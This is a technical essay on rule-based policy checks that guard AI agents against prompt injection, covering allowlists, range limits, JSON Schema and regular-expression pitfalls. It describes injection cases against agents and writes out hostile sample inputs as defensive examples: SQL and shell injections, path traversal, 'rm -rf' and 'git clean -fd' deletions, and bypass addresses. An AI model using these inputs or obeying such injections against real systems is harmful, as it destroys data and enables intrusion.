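Shi and colleagues tested Progent by counting successful attacks, so their results don't separate the attacks the rules blocked from those the model ignored on its own. GPT-4o powered the agent and wrote the rules. The attack success rate on AgentDojo fell as follows:

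| Setting | Attack success rate |
|---|---|
| No defence | 39.9% |
| Rules written from the user's request and never updated | 2.5% |
| Rules updated during the task, with every expansion approved automatically | 1.0% |
| Rules and expansions reviewed by a careful person | 0% |

An expansion is an update that permits a new call. Approving every expansion is meant to represent a careless user, which makes the 1.0% more impressive. Most of the reduction comes from the initial rules, before any updates. The last row shows the most that review can add, because the reviewer never granted unrestricted use of sensitive tools such as `send_money` and rejected every malicious address.

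Only 6% of Progent's rule updates on AgentDojo were expansions and would have needed approval. This suggests that a user would see few prompts, but the number of prompts per task also depends on how often Progent updates its rules.

On Agent Security Bench (ASB), which has ten agent scenarios, the attack success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools, so the LLM put them on the list. Shi and colleagues doubt that a person could tell them apart without knowing which tools to trust. When they wrote rules by hand with that knowledge, the rate fell to 0%. An organisation that installs its own tools should know which ones to trust, so it could easily add a fixed list of trusted tools to the rules for each task.

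Shi and colleagues say that Progent maintained the agent's success on benign tasks on both benchmarks, and that any loss with other agent models was marginal. Their AgentDojo setup helped, because a fixed rule permitted non-sensitive, read-only tools in every task. They also tested a defence in which an LLM chooses which tools to permit, without checking the tools' arguments. It stopped fewer attacks than Progent and caused more benign tasks to fail, much as the tool lists did on Toolathlon.

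The GPT-4o version dates from August 2024, and some later models resist injections much better without any rules. With Claude Sonnet 4 as the agent, 6.8% of attacks succeeded with no defence and 0.5% with Progent. That is still a reduction of more than 90%, but the rules prevent about six successful attacks per hundred attempts, compared with 39 for GPT-4o. Progent's 1.0% also can't be compared with the 5% to 7% of AgentDojo attacks that Sapien's rules permit, because Progent's figure is the share of attacks that succeeded against one model, while Sapien's is the share that would be possible against any model that followed the injected instructions.

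An attacker who knows about Progent could target the LLM that updates the rules. Shi and colleagues tried three such attacks, including injected text telling the LLM to permit the tools the attack needed. With automatic approval still on, these attacks raised the success rate only slightly. That is encouraging, but three attacks are not many, and approving every expansion automatically is an obvious weakness that a better attack could exploit.

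### Value lists learned from past runs

Another way to build a value list is to collect values the agent has used legitimately before. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues, 2026) builds one from records of benign runs. Each entry is a triple of tool, argument and value, such as `send_email`, `to` and Alice's address. The paper treats 21 argument names as sensitive, and the list covers 16 of them, including recipients, account numbers, passwords, file identifiers and product identifiers.

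They leave out the other five: `amount`, `otp` (a one-time password), `body`, `content` and `url`. A one-time password is different every time, amounts vary from one session to the next, and almost every email body is new, so an allowlist of past bodies would block nearly every future email. Sequeira and colleagues put full web addresses in the same group. Site names repeat far more often, so an allowlist of sites might work, but it would permit every page on those sites.

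In Agent-Sentry, the list is the second of three checks. A classifier first examines the order of the calls and where each argument's value came from. If the classifier cannot decide, the list allows the call if its values are listed and come from trusted sources. An LLM judge decides the rest, including any call that has no listable arguments. With the stronger of two classifiers, the whole system allowed 96.4% of benign runs and blocked 96.8% of attacks on a benchmark that Sequeira and colleagues built. The list settled only 0.8% of the decisions, so these results are weak evidence of how well a learned list would work alone.

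Sequeira and colleagues also tested value lists when they compared their system with Progent. They gave Progent one fixed set of rules per agent, which is not how Shi and colleagues recommend using it, and updated its lists from the benign runs in the benchmark. Progent then blocked 97.7% of attacks but allowed only 69.2% of benign runs. On the smaller set of tasks that come with AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, AgentDyn, it blocked 88.4% of attacks and allowed 93.7% of benign runs. Sequeira and colleagues had some reason to make a rival system look bad, and they wrote part of the policies themselves. The test is still a useful measurement of fixed lists, whose false-positive rate rose from 6.3% to 30.8% when the tasks became more varied.

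In one example, the user sometimes asks the agent to email a colleague named Lily. In other tasks, the user asks it to delete a calendar event, and an injection tells it to send Lily a message written by the attacker. An allowlist of recipients that includes Lily lets the injected email through, but one that omits her blocks the emails the user requested. Agent-Sentry passes the injected call to its judge because Lily's address came from untrusted text, and the judge blocks it because the user's request does not mention an email. A separate list of allowed tools for each task would also stop the call, since deleting an event does not require `send_email`.

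### How often a learned list blocks a new value

Suppose the office agent's owner permits payments only to the recipients of the last 1,000 legitimate payments. The check will block the next legitimate payment if it goes to someone new. How often should she expect this to happen?

If she estimates each recipient's share of future payments by dividing past payments to that recipient by 1,000, she will underestimate the share going to new recipients. Anyone who is not in the history gets a share of zero, so the list appears to block no legitimate payments. Gale and Sampson point out in *Good–Turing Frequency Estimation Without Tears* that simple estimates like this can be wildly inaccurate. They explain a better family of methods, which I. J. Good and Alan Turing developed.

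Write $p_v$ for the probability that a payment goes to recipient $v$, and $M_n$ for the total probability of all recipients who do not appear in the first $n$ payments. $M_n$ is the chance that the next legitimate payment is unlisted. The Good–Turing estimate is

$$\hat{M}_n = \frac{N_1}{n},$$

where $N_1$ is the number of recipients who appear exactly once. If 40 recipients appear once in the 1,000 payments, the estimate is $40/1000$, or 4%. At 50 payments a week, the list would block about two legitimate ones.

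*Missing mass problem and Good-Turing estimator* (Hsu, 2025) explains the formula by leaving out one observation at a time. If the list is built from 999 of the 1,000 payments, it fails to cover the remaining payment only if that recipient appears nowhere else in the history. Repeating this for all 1,000 payments therefore produces exactly $N_1$ failures, one for each recipient who was paid once.

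The algebra agrees. Recipient $v$ appears exactly once in $n$ independent payments with probability $n p_v (1-p_v)^{n-1}$. Adding this up over all recipients and dividing by $n$ gives

$$\mathbb{E}\!\left[\frac{N_1}{n}\right] = \sum_v p_v (1-p_v)^{n-1} = \mathbb{E}[M_{n-1}].$$

On average, then, the estimate is exactly right for a list built from one payment fewer. With 1,000 payments, the difference is less than a tenth of a percentage point. The formula does not use the length of the list, so a firm with 60 regular suppliers and one with 400 get the same estimate if each has 40 one-time recipients in the same number of payments. An allowlist is useless for email bodies because, if every past body is different, $N_1 = n$ and the estimate is 100%.

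A single estimate can be inaccurate when the history is short. *Statistical estimation for Large Numbers of Rare Events* reports a simulation with five samples, each of 100 random draws from the whole numbers 1 to 1,000. The Good–Turing estimates of the unseen share ranged from 84% to 96%. The true share was always between 90% and 91%, because each sample contained between 92 and 98 different numbers. In the payment example, chance alone could move the 4% by a percentage point or more.

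A call with several listed arguments is blocked if any one of them has a new value. If 4% of recipients and 3% of account references are new, the check will block between 4% and 7% of legitimate calls, depending on how often both are new in the same call. If the system escalates unlisted values to a judge, as Agent-Sentry does, the estimate gives the number of extra decisions for the judge, not the number of false positives.

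The larger danger is that future payments may not resemble past ones. The formula assumes independent draws from a distribution that stays the same. If the firm makes 200 payments next month, including a refund to each of 30 new customers, the list will block the first payment to each new customer. Those are 15% of the month's payments, and no one could have predicted that from the payment history. Agent-Sentry's results show how much such a change can matter. With its stronger classifier, the system allowed 96.4% of benign runs when it had learned from similar ones, but only 64.4% on AgentDojo's and AgentDyn's own tasks when it had learned only from the other benchmark. Those figures are for all three checks together, so the list accounts for only part of the drop.

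The formula's estimate is also too low when payments come in groups. Suppose the firm pays every new contractor twice, once as a deposit and once on completion. No contractor appears exactly once in the finished history, so they add nothing to $N_1$, yet the list would have blocked every deposit. A safer test is to keep the payments in order, build the list from the first 800, and count how many of the last 200 it would have blocked. This accounts for both steady growth in new recipients and payments in groups, but not for changes that haven't begun.

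Testing a list on the same runs that produced it is much worse than either method, because the list already contains every value in those runs. Sequeira and colleagues report that one version of their system, with its weaker classifier, blocked 10.7% of benign runs that it had not been fitted on, but only 0.2% when they fitted and tested it on the same runs. They reused the runs to match the knowledge of the benchmark that Progent's rules contain, which is a fair reason, but nobody should expect a rate of 0.2% on new work.

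A learned list also depends on a clean history. If an earlier injection got one payment through to Eve and nobody noticed, the list will permit her from then on. The owner could require two payments before a recipient joins the list, but this would raise the false-positive rate, by an amount the leave-one-out argument can also estimate. A removed payment now passes only if its recipient appears at least twice among the remaining 999, so both payments to any recipient with exactly two also fail. If there are $N_2$ such recipients, that adds $2N_2$ failures. With 15 of them, the expected false-positive rate rises from 4% to 7%. Since only 40 recipients appear once, it may be easier for somebody to read through their names instead.

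## Range constraints: bounding numbers, dates and lengths

A list of past values does not work for payment amounts, because almost every payment is for a different sum. A range constraint instead permits every value between two bounds, including values the agent has never used. If $f(x)$ is a number computed from the call $x$, the rule is

$$\text{allow } x \text{ only if } a \le f(x) \le b.$$

In the office agent's `pay` rule, $f(x)$ is the amount. In other rules, it could be the number of characters in an email, the number of days between an invoice date and today, or the number of times the agent has called a tool in the current session.

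### Bounds in JSON Schema

Models usually write tool calls in JSON, a text format for structured data, and developers often describe a tool's arguments in JSON Schema, a language for stating what JSON data must look like. A schema for `pay` can therefore include some range constraints:

```
{
  "type": "object",
  "required": ["recipient", "amount", "currency"],
  "properties": {
    "recipient": { "type": "string", "maxLength": 100 },
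    "amount":    { "type": "number", "exclusiveMinimum": 0, "maximum": 500 },
    "currency":  { "const": "EUR" }
  }
}
```

*JSON Schema Validation* (Wright, Andrews and Hutton, 2020) defines `maximum` as inclusive, so a payment of exactly 500 passes when the maximum is 500. `exclusiveMinimum` is strict, so a payment of zero fails when it is set to 0. `maxLength` limits the number of characters in a text and `maxItems` the number of entries in a list, and each has a matching minimum.

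Each of these keywords applies to only one type of value. `maximum` has no effect on text, so without `"type": "number"` the text `"90000"` would pass. The conditions on `amount` also have no effect if the call omits `amount`, so the schema needs the `required` line.

Dates are harder to bound because JSON stores them as text. The `format` keyword can label text as a date, but by default a validator (the program that applies the schema) doesn't check that the text matches the label. Wright and colleagues also define no keyword for an earliest or latest date. A schema can't count earlier calls either, so date ranges and call counts both need ordinary code in the policy check.

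### Why respelling a number doesn't help an attacker

A bound on a properly typed number compares values rather than characters. `90000`, `90000.0` and `9e4` are the same number, and *JSON Schema* (Dusseault, Wright and Andrews, 2026), a draft of a future standard, requires validators to give equal values the same result. A text rule that enforces a limit by forbidding four digits in a row would block `90000` but miss `9e4`. It would also block `450.0000`, which is within the limit.

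Some evidence for this comes from web security. *WAPP* (2026) describes a system that learns rules for web requests, not for agents' tool calls. In its tests, five of eleven variants of known attacks got past a widely used set of attack signatures. A learned rule that permitted only integers in a page-number field blocked all five. Five strings are a small sample, but the result is unsurprising, because a script written in different characters is still not an integer.

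The range check and the tool must read the same number. According to Dusseault and colleagues, the behaviour is undefined if a call contains `amount` twice. The check might read the first value, 50, while the tool pays the second, 50,000. The software can prevent this by parsing the call once and giving the tool the checked values instead of the original text.

An attacker doesn't need to respell a number that is already in range, such as Eve's 450 euros. The bound limits the size of each payment but not who receives it, so the `pay` rule also needs an allowlist of recipients.

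### How one payment gets past a limit

A numeric bound in JSON Schema doesn't apply to text, so if the developer leaves out the number type and the model writes the amount as text, the call passes the bound, and the payment tool may then convert the amount to a number and pay. A hand-written check could also fail if it compares the amount and the limit as text, because "10000" comes before "500" in alphabetical order. Strict typing fixes both problems. The JSON Schema guide shows that a schema requiring a number rejects `"42"`. Strict typing may also block a benign payment because the model wrote the amount as text. Returning an error that the amount must be a number should usually let the agent correct the call, or the software can convert the text first and check the result.

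The rule also has to require the currency and specify which one is allowed, as the schema above does. If the call omits the currency and the tool fills in a default, or if the rule checks only `amount`, then 500 Kuwaiti dinars, worth well over 1,000 euros, will pass a limit meant for euros. The limit must also be in the unit the tool expects. If the tool expects cents but the rule's author was thinking in euros, a limit of 500 blocks every payment above five euros. Conversely, a limit of 50,000 meant as cents permits a payment of 50,000 euros if the tool expects euros.

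Negative amounts get past a rule that has only an upper bound. MITRE's *CWE-839*, another entry in its catalogue of software weaknesses, gives the example of a bank account with a withdrawal limit of 350. The program checks that the withdrawal is below the limit, then subtracts it from the balance, so a withdrawal of −1,000 passes and adds 1,000 to the account. The fix is to add a lower bound. MITRE's corrected code still requires the withdrawal to be strictly less than 350, so a customer who asks for exactly the maximum gets an error wrongly saying that the amount exceeds it. People often pay round sums, so this kind of mistake can cause more false positives than one might expect.

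Computer arithmetic uses NaN, "not a number", for undefined results such as zero divided by zero. Standard JSON has no NaN, but some parsers accept it, including Python's by default. Every greater-than or less-than comparison with NaN is false, so a rule that blocks amounts above 500 lets NaN through. The office agent's rule blocks NaN because it allows a payment only when the amount is above 0 and at most 500.

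MITRE notes that attackers may also use rounding errors in financial calculations to steal money. Adding `"multipleOf": 0.01` to the schema rules out fractions of a cent, but it can also block legitimate payments. In ordinary double-precision arithmetic, 19.99 divided by 0.01 is 1998.9999999999998, so a validator that does this division and requires a whole number will reject a payment of 19.99. The JSON Schema guide tells developers not to worry about the usual limits of floating-point arithmetic, which is true of the specification but not necessarily of the validator. Storing amounts as a whole number of cents avoids the problem.

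### Limits that depend on more than the call

The bounds so far are fixed, so the check needs only the arguments. *AgentPolicyForge* (Shang, Du and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that builds test cases for policy checks. The system writes each condition in a more general form, $\phi(\text{args}, s)$, where $s$ is the state of the environment before the call. One of its templates is "Each [operation] must not exceed [limit]". Filling in a transfer tool, its amount argument and a limit of 500 produces "Each transfer must not exceed $500" and code that compares the amount with 500.

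That condition doesn't depend on $s$, but a rule that a transfer must not exceed the account's balance does, so the same call may pass in the morning and fail in the afternoon. JSON Schema can't express this rule because Dusseault and colleagues forbid verdicts that depend on anything except the schema and the input. The check must itself look up the balance from a source the agent can't alter.

Other policies in *AgentPolicyForge* show how easily a simple range goes wrong:

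- One bans transfers between 21:00 and 05:00 UTC. No hour is both at least 21 and less than 5, so a check that joins the two conditions with "and" never blocks anything. It needs "or".
- Another says that an entry must not be dated more than 30 days in the past. By itself, this permits an entry dated ten years in the future.
- A third bans manual operations on account IDs below 1,000. Account 999 is not slightly more dangerous than account 1,000, so this range is really a blocklist in shorter form.
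- A fourth requires any operation above $1,000 to include an approval field. An agent under an attacker's control could simply fill in the field, and Shang and colleagues acknowledge that the rule does not verify independent approval by two people.

Shang and colleagues also measured how well models enforce such policies. With the policy in its prompt, an agent running on Claude Sonnet 5 still carried out a forbidden call in 13% to 15% of the test cases designed to cause one, and refused about 9% of benign requests. A separate guard model that they trained reduced forbidden calls to about 8% and refusals of benign requests to 6% to 7%. These figures cover all ten kinds of policy, so the rates for transfer limits alone may differ. They did not compare the guard with complete executable checks, though they say that such checks can be used directly where they exist. One line of code can enforce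 a $500 limit, so there seems to be little reason to accept an 8% failure rate there.

Every violation in their tests is visible in a single call, which leaves out an obvious attack on a transfer limit. Twenty payments of 450 euros each satisfy the office agent's rule, and together they send Eve 9,000. Stopping this requires a cumulative limit,

$$S + \text{amount} \le C,$$

where $S$ is the total already paid in some period and $C$ is the most the agent may pay in that period. This is a simple rule over a sequence of calls, and it needs memory. If the check forgets $S$ when a session ends, an attacker can start again in the next one. The choice of period also matters. With a limit of 1,000 per calendar day, the agent could pay 1,000 just before midnight and another 1,000 just after, while a limit over any 24 hours would prevent that. Two payments that arrive together may also both pass if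 the check reads the old total twice, so it should reserve the money before each payment runs.

A cumulative limit also produces false positives. If Eve has already received 900 of the day's 1,000 euros, a legitimate payment of 300 to a supplier will fail. The same can happen without an attacker at the end of the month, when many invoices fall due together. Testing each benign payment against an empty history would miss these false positives.

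### Length limits taken from tool schemas

*Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes ARM, a system that sits between an agent and its tools and automatically derives some bounds from each tool's schema. It limits text arguments with names like `note`, `comment`, `metadata` or `description` to 100 characters, and optional text arguments to 50. These limits are meant to stop an attacker from sending stolen data in fields where nobody looks for it. ARM also applies fixed limits of 10,000 characters for any text argument and 100 calls per tool per session.

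A limit of 100 characters would cut off quite ordinary notes. If the office agent's payment tool had a `note` field, it could not send this one, which has 102:

```
Invoice 2026-0417 for stationery, delivered 3 September, less credit note 2026-0391 for returned paper
```

Meeting agendas and bug reports are usually much longer. The 50-character limit may be worse, because whether an argument is optional has little to do with how long it should be. An optional `cc` field that takes all its addresses as one string could hold Alice's and Bob's, but not `carla@client.example` as well. Many web addresses and file paths also exceed 50 characters.

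It is less clear what the limits prevent. Many passwords and access keys have fewer than 50 characters, which is presumably why ARM also searches for known key formats. An attacker can split longer data across calls, since 100 calls with a 100-character note each can carry 10,000 characters. In one of Chinaei's scenarios, ARM blocks the agent from reading a protected password file, and the agent then emails "shadow file exists" to the attacker, which at 18 characters (the paper counts 14) passes every length check. ARM still blocks the email, because it follows a blocked call.

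Chinaei tested three attacks, but both versions of the system he compared used the same length limits, so the tests don't show whether those limits stop anything. He also says his evaluation does not establish false-positive rates. The figures of 100 and 50 are best treated as starting points to compare with the lengths of a tool's past legitimate arguments.

### Learning a bound from past calls

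*WAPP*'s system learns its rules from live web traffic. By default, it waits for at least 50 successful requests to a page, from at least 50 addresses and over at least 12 hours. It then works out each field's type, range and permitted characters, and whether the field is required. In a test on two web applications, the rules blocked 33% to 47% of legitimate requests to text fields, but none to integer fields or other fields with a restricted format.

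The false positives came from a punctuation rule, not the ranges. The system permits a punctuation mark only if it appears in at least 90% of a field's past values, so it blocked the comment "Great product, arrived on time!" because of the comma and the exclamation mark. Integer fields had no false positives, which is encouraging, but the test covered whole rules, so it doesn't show how well the numeric ranges would do by themselves. The samples were also small. In another of the paper's tests, a comment field had no false positives among 15 legitimate values, but 13 among a different set of 50.

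The expected false-positive rate of a learned bound can be worked out in advance. Suppose the office agent's owner sets the payment limit at the largest of the last $n$ legitimate payments. Assume that the past payments and the next one are exchangeable, meaning that every order of the $n+1$ amounts is equally likely, and that no two are equal. Each amount is then equally likely to be the largest, so

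$$P(\text{the next payment exceeds the limit}) = \frac{1}{n+1}.$$

For $n = 500$, this is 1/501, or about 0.2%. Good–Turing estimates for value lists depend on how often values repeat, but you only need $n$ for this result. If some amounts are equal, the probability can only be lower, because a payment equal to the largest passes. A learned lower bound adds another $1/(n+1)$.

The figure is an average over possible histories. If payments are independent, about one history in twenty will produce a limit that blocks 0.6% or more of future payments.

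The owner may prefer a tighter limit. Setting it at the $k$-th largest past payment blocks the next one with probability $k/(n+1)$, by the same argument. With $k = 5$ and $n = 500$, the limit is roughly the 99th percentile and blocks about 1% of benign payments by design. It is also more robust to a contaminated history, because one fraudulent payment of 50,000 raises the largest value to 50,000, but it would take five to raise the fifth largest that far. The false-positive rate doesn't reveal this problem, because a looser limit blocks fewer legitimate payments. Similarly, *WAPP* found that when 0.5% of the training requests for a username field were malicious, the learned rule let half the test attacks through and still blocked no legitimate usernames.

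The $1/(n+1)$ result still holds when payments are heavy-tailed, meaning that a few are far larger than the rest, but the limit becomes much less useful. Suppose that every payment is at least 10 euros and that, from there up, each doubling of the amount halves the share of payments above it. Half of all payments are then below 20 euros, but the largest of 500 will typically be around 7,200. A limit set there blocks only about 0.14% of legitimate payments but lets Eve take 7,200 euros at a time. Lowering the limit to the 99th percentile, 1,000 euros, cuts her largest payment by a factor of about seven but blocks about seven times as many legitimate payments.

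A safety margin also helps less when payment amounts have a heavy tail. With an exponential distribution, where very large payments are much rarer, doubling the limit reduces the expected false-positive rate from 1 in 501 to about 1 in 126,000. In the heavy-tailed example, doubling the limit only reduces the rate to 1 in 1,002. The few legitimate payments that the limit blocks are also the largest, and these may matter most to the business.

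The result does not hold under inflation, because later payments tend to be larger and the amounts are no longer exchangeable. The effect can be small when payments vary widely in size, but it can be severe for a regular payment close to the limit. Suppose the largest payment in the history is a monthly rent of 480 euros. If the landlord raises it by 5%, to 504, a learned limit of 480 will block it every month until somebody changes the limit, and so will the office agent's hand-written limit of 500.

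Learned bounds work worst for values that always increase. A learned upper bound on invoice numbers would block every new invoice, and a learned latest date would block every call dated after the history ends. A date rule should therefore limit how many days a date can be before or after today, and take today's date from the check's own clock rather than from the call.

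## Regular expressions: constraining the form of text

Text has no useful upper or lower bound, but paths, addresses and order numbers usually have a predictable form that a regular expression can describe. Most characters in a regular expression stand for themselves. `[a-z]` stands for any one lower-case letter, `+` means one or more of the preceding item, `*` zero or more, and `{6}` exactly six. `^` marks the start of the text and `$` the end. A dot stands for almost any character, so a literal dot needs a backslash, as in `\.txt`.

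Write $L(p)$ for the set of texts that the pattern $p$ describes from first character to last. A rule can use $p$ as a required form,

$$\text{allow } s \text{ only if } s \in L(p),$$

or as a forbidden pattern,

$$\text{block } s \text{ if some part of } s \text{ is in } L(p).$$

A regex that paths must match works like an allowlist. Suppose the office agent may read only paths that match `^/office/shared/[a-z0-9_]+\.txt$`. The brackets contain no slash or dot, so the rule rejects `/office/shared/../payroll.txt`, which leads out of the shared folder, even if the rule's author never anticipated it. The rule also rejects `/office/shared/Minutes-March.txt`, because the filename contains capitals and a hyphen. A regex that paths must not match works like a blocklist. A rule against `payroll` lets the March minutes through, but it also lets `salaries.txt` through.

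A regular expression can specify the form a value must have or a pattern it must not match. In theory the two approaches are interchangeable, because for every regular expression there is another that matches exactly the texts the first does not. In practice, whoever writes a required form has to think of the legitimate values, while whoever writes a forbidden pattern has to think of the attacks.

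### Searching for a match and matching the whole text

Suppose the office agent also has a tool `get_order(order_id)`, and order numbers look like `ORD-204815`. The pattern `ORD-[0-9]{6}` describes them correctly. But many regex functions search, which means they succeed if any part of the text matches, so they also accept these:

```
ORD-2048157
ORD-204815' OR '1'='1
```

The extra digit in the top line is probably a typing error. The other line is an attack on a tool that pastes the order number into a database query. The added condition is always true, so the query may return every order. MITRE gives a similar example, in which a search for digits, a hyphen and more digits accepts `; ls -l ; echo 123-456`. The anchored pattern `^ORD-[0-9]{6}$` rejects all three strings. It still accepts another customer's order number, because that number has the right form.

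Email domains are easier to get wrong. Suppose the owner wants the agent to send email only to addresses at `firm.example`, and the check searches for a match.

| Pattern | An outside recipient that it lets through |
|---|---|
| `firm\.example` | `eve@firm.example.evil.example` |
| `firm\.example$` | `eve@notfirm.example` |
| `@firm\.example$` | `eve@evil.example,bob@firm.example` |
| `^[a-z.]+@firm\.example$` | None of these |

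The attack in the third row works if the mail tool splits the text at the comma and sends to both addresses. Leaving out a backslash can also let in the wrong domain. If the firm's addresses end in `mail.firm.example`, a pattern without backslashes before the dots also accepts `mail-firm.example`, a different domain that anyone might register. Anchors may also cover only part of a pattern. In `^alice@firm\.example|bob@firm\.example$`, where the bar means "or", the `^` applies only to Alice's address and the `$` only to Bob's, so `alice@firm.example.evil.example` passes. Putting parentheses around the two addresses fixes this.

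JSON Schema's `pattern` keyword accepts a string if any part of it matches the regular expression. Wright and colleagues state that regular expressions are "not implicitly anchored", and Dusseault and colleagues keep that rule in their draft. Test data in Go's code for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools, includes a case in which the pattern `a+` must accept `xxaayy`. XML Schema, an older standard for XML data, requires the whole value to match, so a pattern copied from it into JSON Schema becomes looser without any error message. Shi and colleagues built Progent's rules on JSON Schema, so the anchors in the office agent's path rule are presumably necessary.

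MITRE's *CWE-777*, "Regular Expression without Anchors", describes a web page that checks a language name by searching for `[A-Za-z0-9]+` and then loads a file of that name. Any text containing a letter or digit passes, including `../../etc/passwd`. Another example checks an internet address before contacting it. MITRE warns that this check accepts `0x63.63.63.63`, which the network tool reads as a different address. But the printed code uses Python's `match` function, which only matches from the first character, so it rejects that text. Python's `search` function would accept it. The printed code does accept `63.63.63.63.evil.example`, because the pattern has no anchor at the end.

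These errors still occur in security software. GCVE's *CWE-777*, a page in a public vulnerability database, records one from September 2026 in tinyauth that let an attacker get past a rule by appending an allowed route to the request. Some missing anchors are easy to find automatically, and CodeQL's *Missing regular expression anchor* documents a code scanner's warning for them.

The advice to anchor applies to patterns that describe a required form. A pattern that describes forbidden text usually needs to be unanchored, because `^rm` catches `rm -rf /office` but misses `sudo rm -rf /office`, which runs the same deletion with administrator rights.

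### Case, alphabets and engines

Regular expressions are case-sensitive by default. Databases generally treat `DROP TABLE` and `drop table` as the same command, so a forbidden pattern written in capitals misses the lower-case version. When input must match a pattern to be allowed, the same oversight causes false positives. For example, the last pattern in the table above blocks `alice@Firm.example`, even though case doesn't matter in email domains.

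Accented letters and other alphabets cause similar trouble. The range `[A-Za-z]` excludes é, so a customer-name rule that uses it blocks José. Unicode, the standard that numbers characters, can also represent some characters in more than one way. For example, é can be one code point or an e followed by a separate accent. Dusseault and colleagues treat two texts as equal only if their code points match exactly, so a check that follows their rule can treat two identical-looking names as different. Converting text to a canonical form first avoids this.

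Some symbols also mean different things in different engines, the programs that apply regular expressions. In Python, `\d` matches digits from many scripts, including Arabic and Devanagari, while in JavaScript it matches only 0 to 9. Python's `$` also matches just before a final line break, so `^ORD-[0-9]{6}$` accepts an order number with a line break after it. In Ruby, `^` and `$` mark the start and end of a line, so a text of several lines passes if any line has the right form.

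JSON Schema's *Regular Expressions* recommends a limited set of symbols because many engines do not support the full JavaScript syntax. It also notes that JSON has its own escape codes, which matters most for forbidden patterns. The regex `\bdelete\b` matches "delete" as a whole word, but in JSON `\b` means a backspace character. If an author forgets to double the backslashes, the rule matches "delete" only between two backspace characters and will probably never block anything.

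### Why a pattern cannot parse a command

The office agent's `run_command` takes a whole shell command as one piece of text. Compare these two:

```
echo "rm -rf /office"
bash -c "rm -rf /office"
```

The top command prints the quoted words, while the bottom one runs them. An author could write a pattern for this pair, but shell commands can contain other commands, which can contain more. Database queries can nest in the same way.

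A regular expression in the strict sense cannot check whether text is correctly nested if the nesting can go to any depth. A program can match such an expression with a fixed number of internal states, $k$, however long the text is. There are $k+1$ possible runs of 0 to $k$ opening brackets, so at least two of them, with different lengths $i$ and $j$, leave the program in the same state. If the program accepts $i$ opening brackets followed by $i$ closing ones, it therefore also accepts $j$ opening brackets followed by $i$ closing ones, which do not balance.

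Some engines add features that can match nested brackets, and a strict expression can handle nesting up to a fixed depth, though it soon becomes unreadable. Neither can be used to determine what a variable in the command will contain when it runs. Strict expressions also have an advantage for policy checks, because a program can always decide whether one permits everything that another does. No method can decide this in every case once patterns can refer back to text they have already matched. Progent's solver makes this kind of comparison when an LLM proposes new rules.

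This limit matters much less when a regex specifies the form a command must take. The pattern `^git (status|diff|log)$` matches only three commands, none of which contains quotes, brackets or variables, so the rule works without interpreting that syntax. It blocks any command that does use that syntax, including legitimate ones.

The obvious alternative to regular expressions is a parser, a program that works out the structure of a command. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) describes a policy check for agents that instead rewrites shell text in nine fixed ways and then applies regular expressions. Yang avoided a full parser because the shell has many rare edge cases and because developers might be tempted to run nested commands to see what they produce. The edge cases are a real difficulty, but the second reason seems weaker, since a parser can identify a nested command without running it, and Yang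 plans to add a parser.

Better still, the office agent's tool could take a program name and a list of arguments instead of one line of text. Ordinary JSON parsing would then separate them, and each pattern would only have to check one short value. This works only if the tool passes the arguments directly to the program, because joining them into a line for the shell brings the problem back.

### Patterns that take too long to check

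Many engines, including the standard ones in Python and JavaScript, match by backtracking. When an attempt fails, the engine goes back to its last choice and tries another option. MITRE's *CWE-1333* shows how this can go wrong with the pattern `^(\w+\s?)*$`, which is meant to recognise a sentence. `\w` stands for a letter, digit or underscore, and `\s?` for an optional space.

The trouble is the `+` inside the `*`, which lets the engine divide a run of letters into groups in many ways. It can read `abc` as `abc`, `ab`+`c`, `a`+`bc` or `a`+`b`+`c`. A run of $k$ letters has $k-1$ gaps, each of which may or may not be a division, so there are $2^{k-1}$ ways to divide it. Now suppose the text is $n$ letters followed by an exclamation mark. No division can succeed, but a simple backtracking engine tries every division of the first $k$ letters, for every $k$ up to $n$, and tests each time whether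 it has reached the end. With one more test for no letters at all, the total is

$$1 + \sum_{k=1}^{n} 2^{k-1} = 2^n.$$

At 100 million tests a second, twenty letters need about a million tests and take about a hundredth of a second, thirty need about a billion and take about eleven seconds, and forty need about a trillion and take about three hours. MITRE's own sample text, "Bad characters: $@#", needs only about 4,100 tests, so it is too short to do any harm.

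An attacker could exploit such a pattern in a policy check by persuading the agent to write one long argument. When the check runs out of time, the agent stops working if the system blocks the call, and the attacker can bypass every rule if the system lets it through. GCVE's *Common Weakness Enumeration* lists 916 vulnerabilities of this type, including one in validate.js, a library for checking data.

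The pattern's author can often remove the ambiguity. `^(\w+(\s\w+)*\s?)?$` accepts the same sentences but can divide a run of letters in only one way, so thirty letters and an exclamation mark need 31 tests instead of a billion. MITRE also recommends limiting the length of the input and the amount of backtracking. The length check has to run before the pattern, so putting `maxLength` in the same JSON schema may not help, because the validator may apply `pattern` first.

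A more general solution is an engine that does not backtrack. Google's RE2 follows all possible divisions at once as it reads the text, so for a given pattern the time grows only in proportion to the text's length. To achieve this, RE2 omits some features. JFrog's *Configure Tool Policies*, the documentation for a product that uses RE2, says the engine does not support lookaround, which tests the text before or after a point without consuming it. JSON Schema's recommended symbols include one form of lookaround, so RE2 can reject a pattern that follows the recommendation. RE2 also rejects MITRE's corrected version of the sentence pattern, because it uses lookaround and a reference back to earlier text. A policy check should not start if one of its patterns is invalid, since skipping the rule could leave a gap that nobody notices.

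### Harmless calls that contain a forbidden word

A forbidden pattern often matches a call that mentions a dangerous action without performing it. *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents* (Beno, 2026) tests models that judge tool calls on cases including dry runs and deletions quoted in notes. Regular expressions have particular difficulty with these two kinds of cases.

The command `git clean -fd` deletes files that the version-control program git is not tracking. `git clean -n` is a dry run, which only lists the files it would delete. Suppose the office agent's owner first blocks the word `clean`, then narrows the pattern three times as people complain about blocked calls.

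| Command | `clean` | `git clean` | `^git clean` | `^git clean -[a-z]*f` |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Benign: `cat cleaning_rota.txt` | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Benign: `echo "ask before git clean" >> notes.txt` | Blocked | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed |
| Benign: `git clean -n` | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked | Allowed |
| Harmful: `git clean -fd` | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
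| Harmful: `git -C /office clean -fd` | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Harmful: `cd /office && git clean -fd` | Blocked | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed |
| Harmful: `git clean --force -d` | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked | Allowed |
| Correct verdicts | 4 of 7 | 4 of 7 | 4 of 7 | 4 of 7 |

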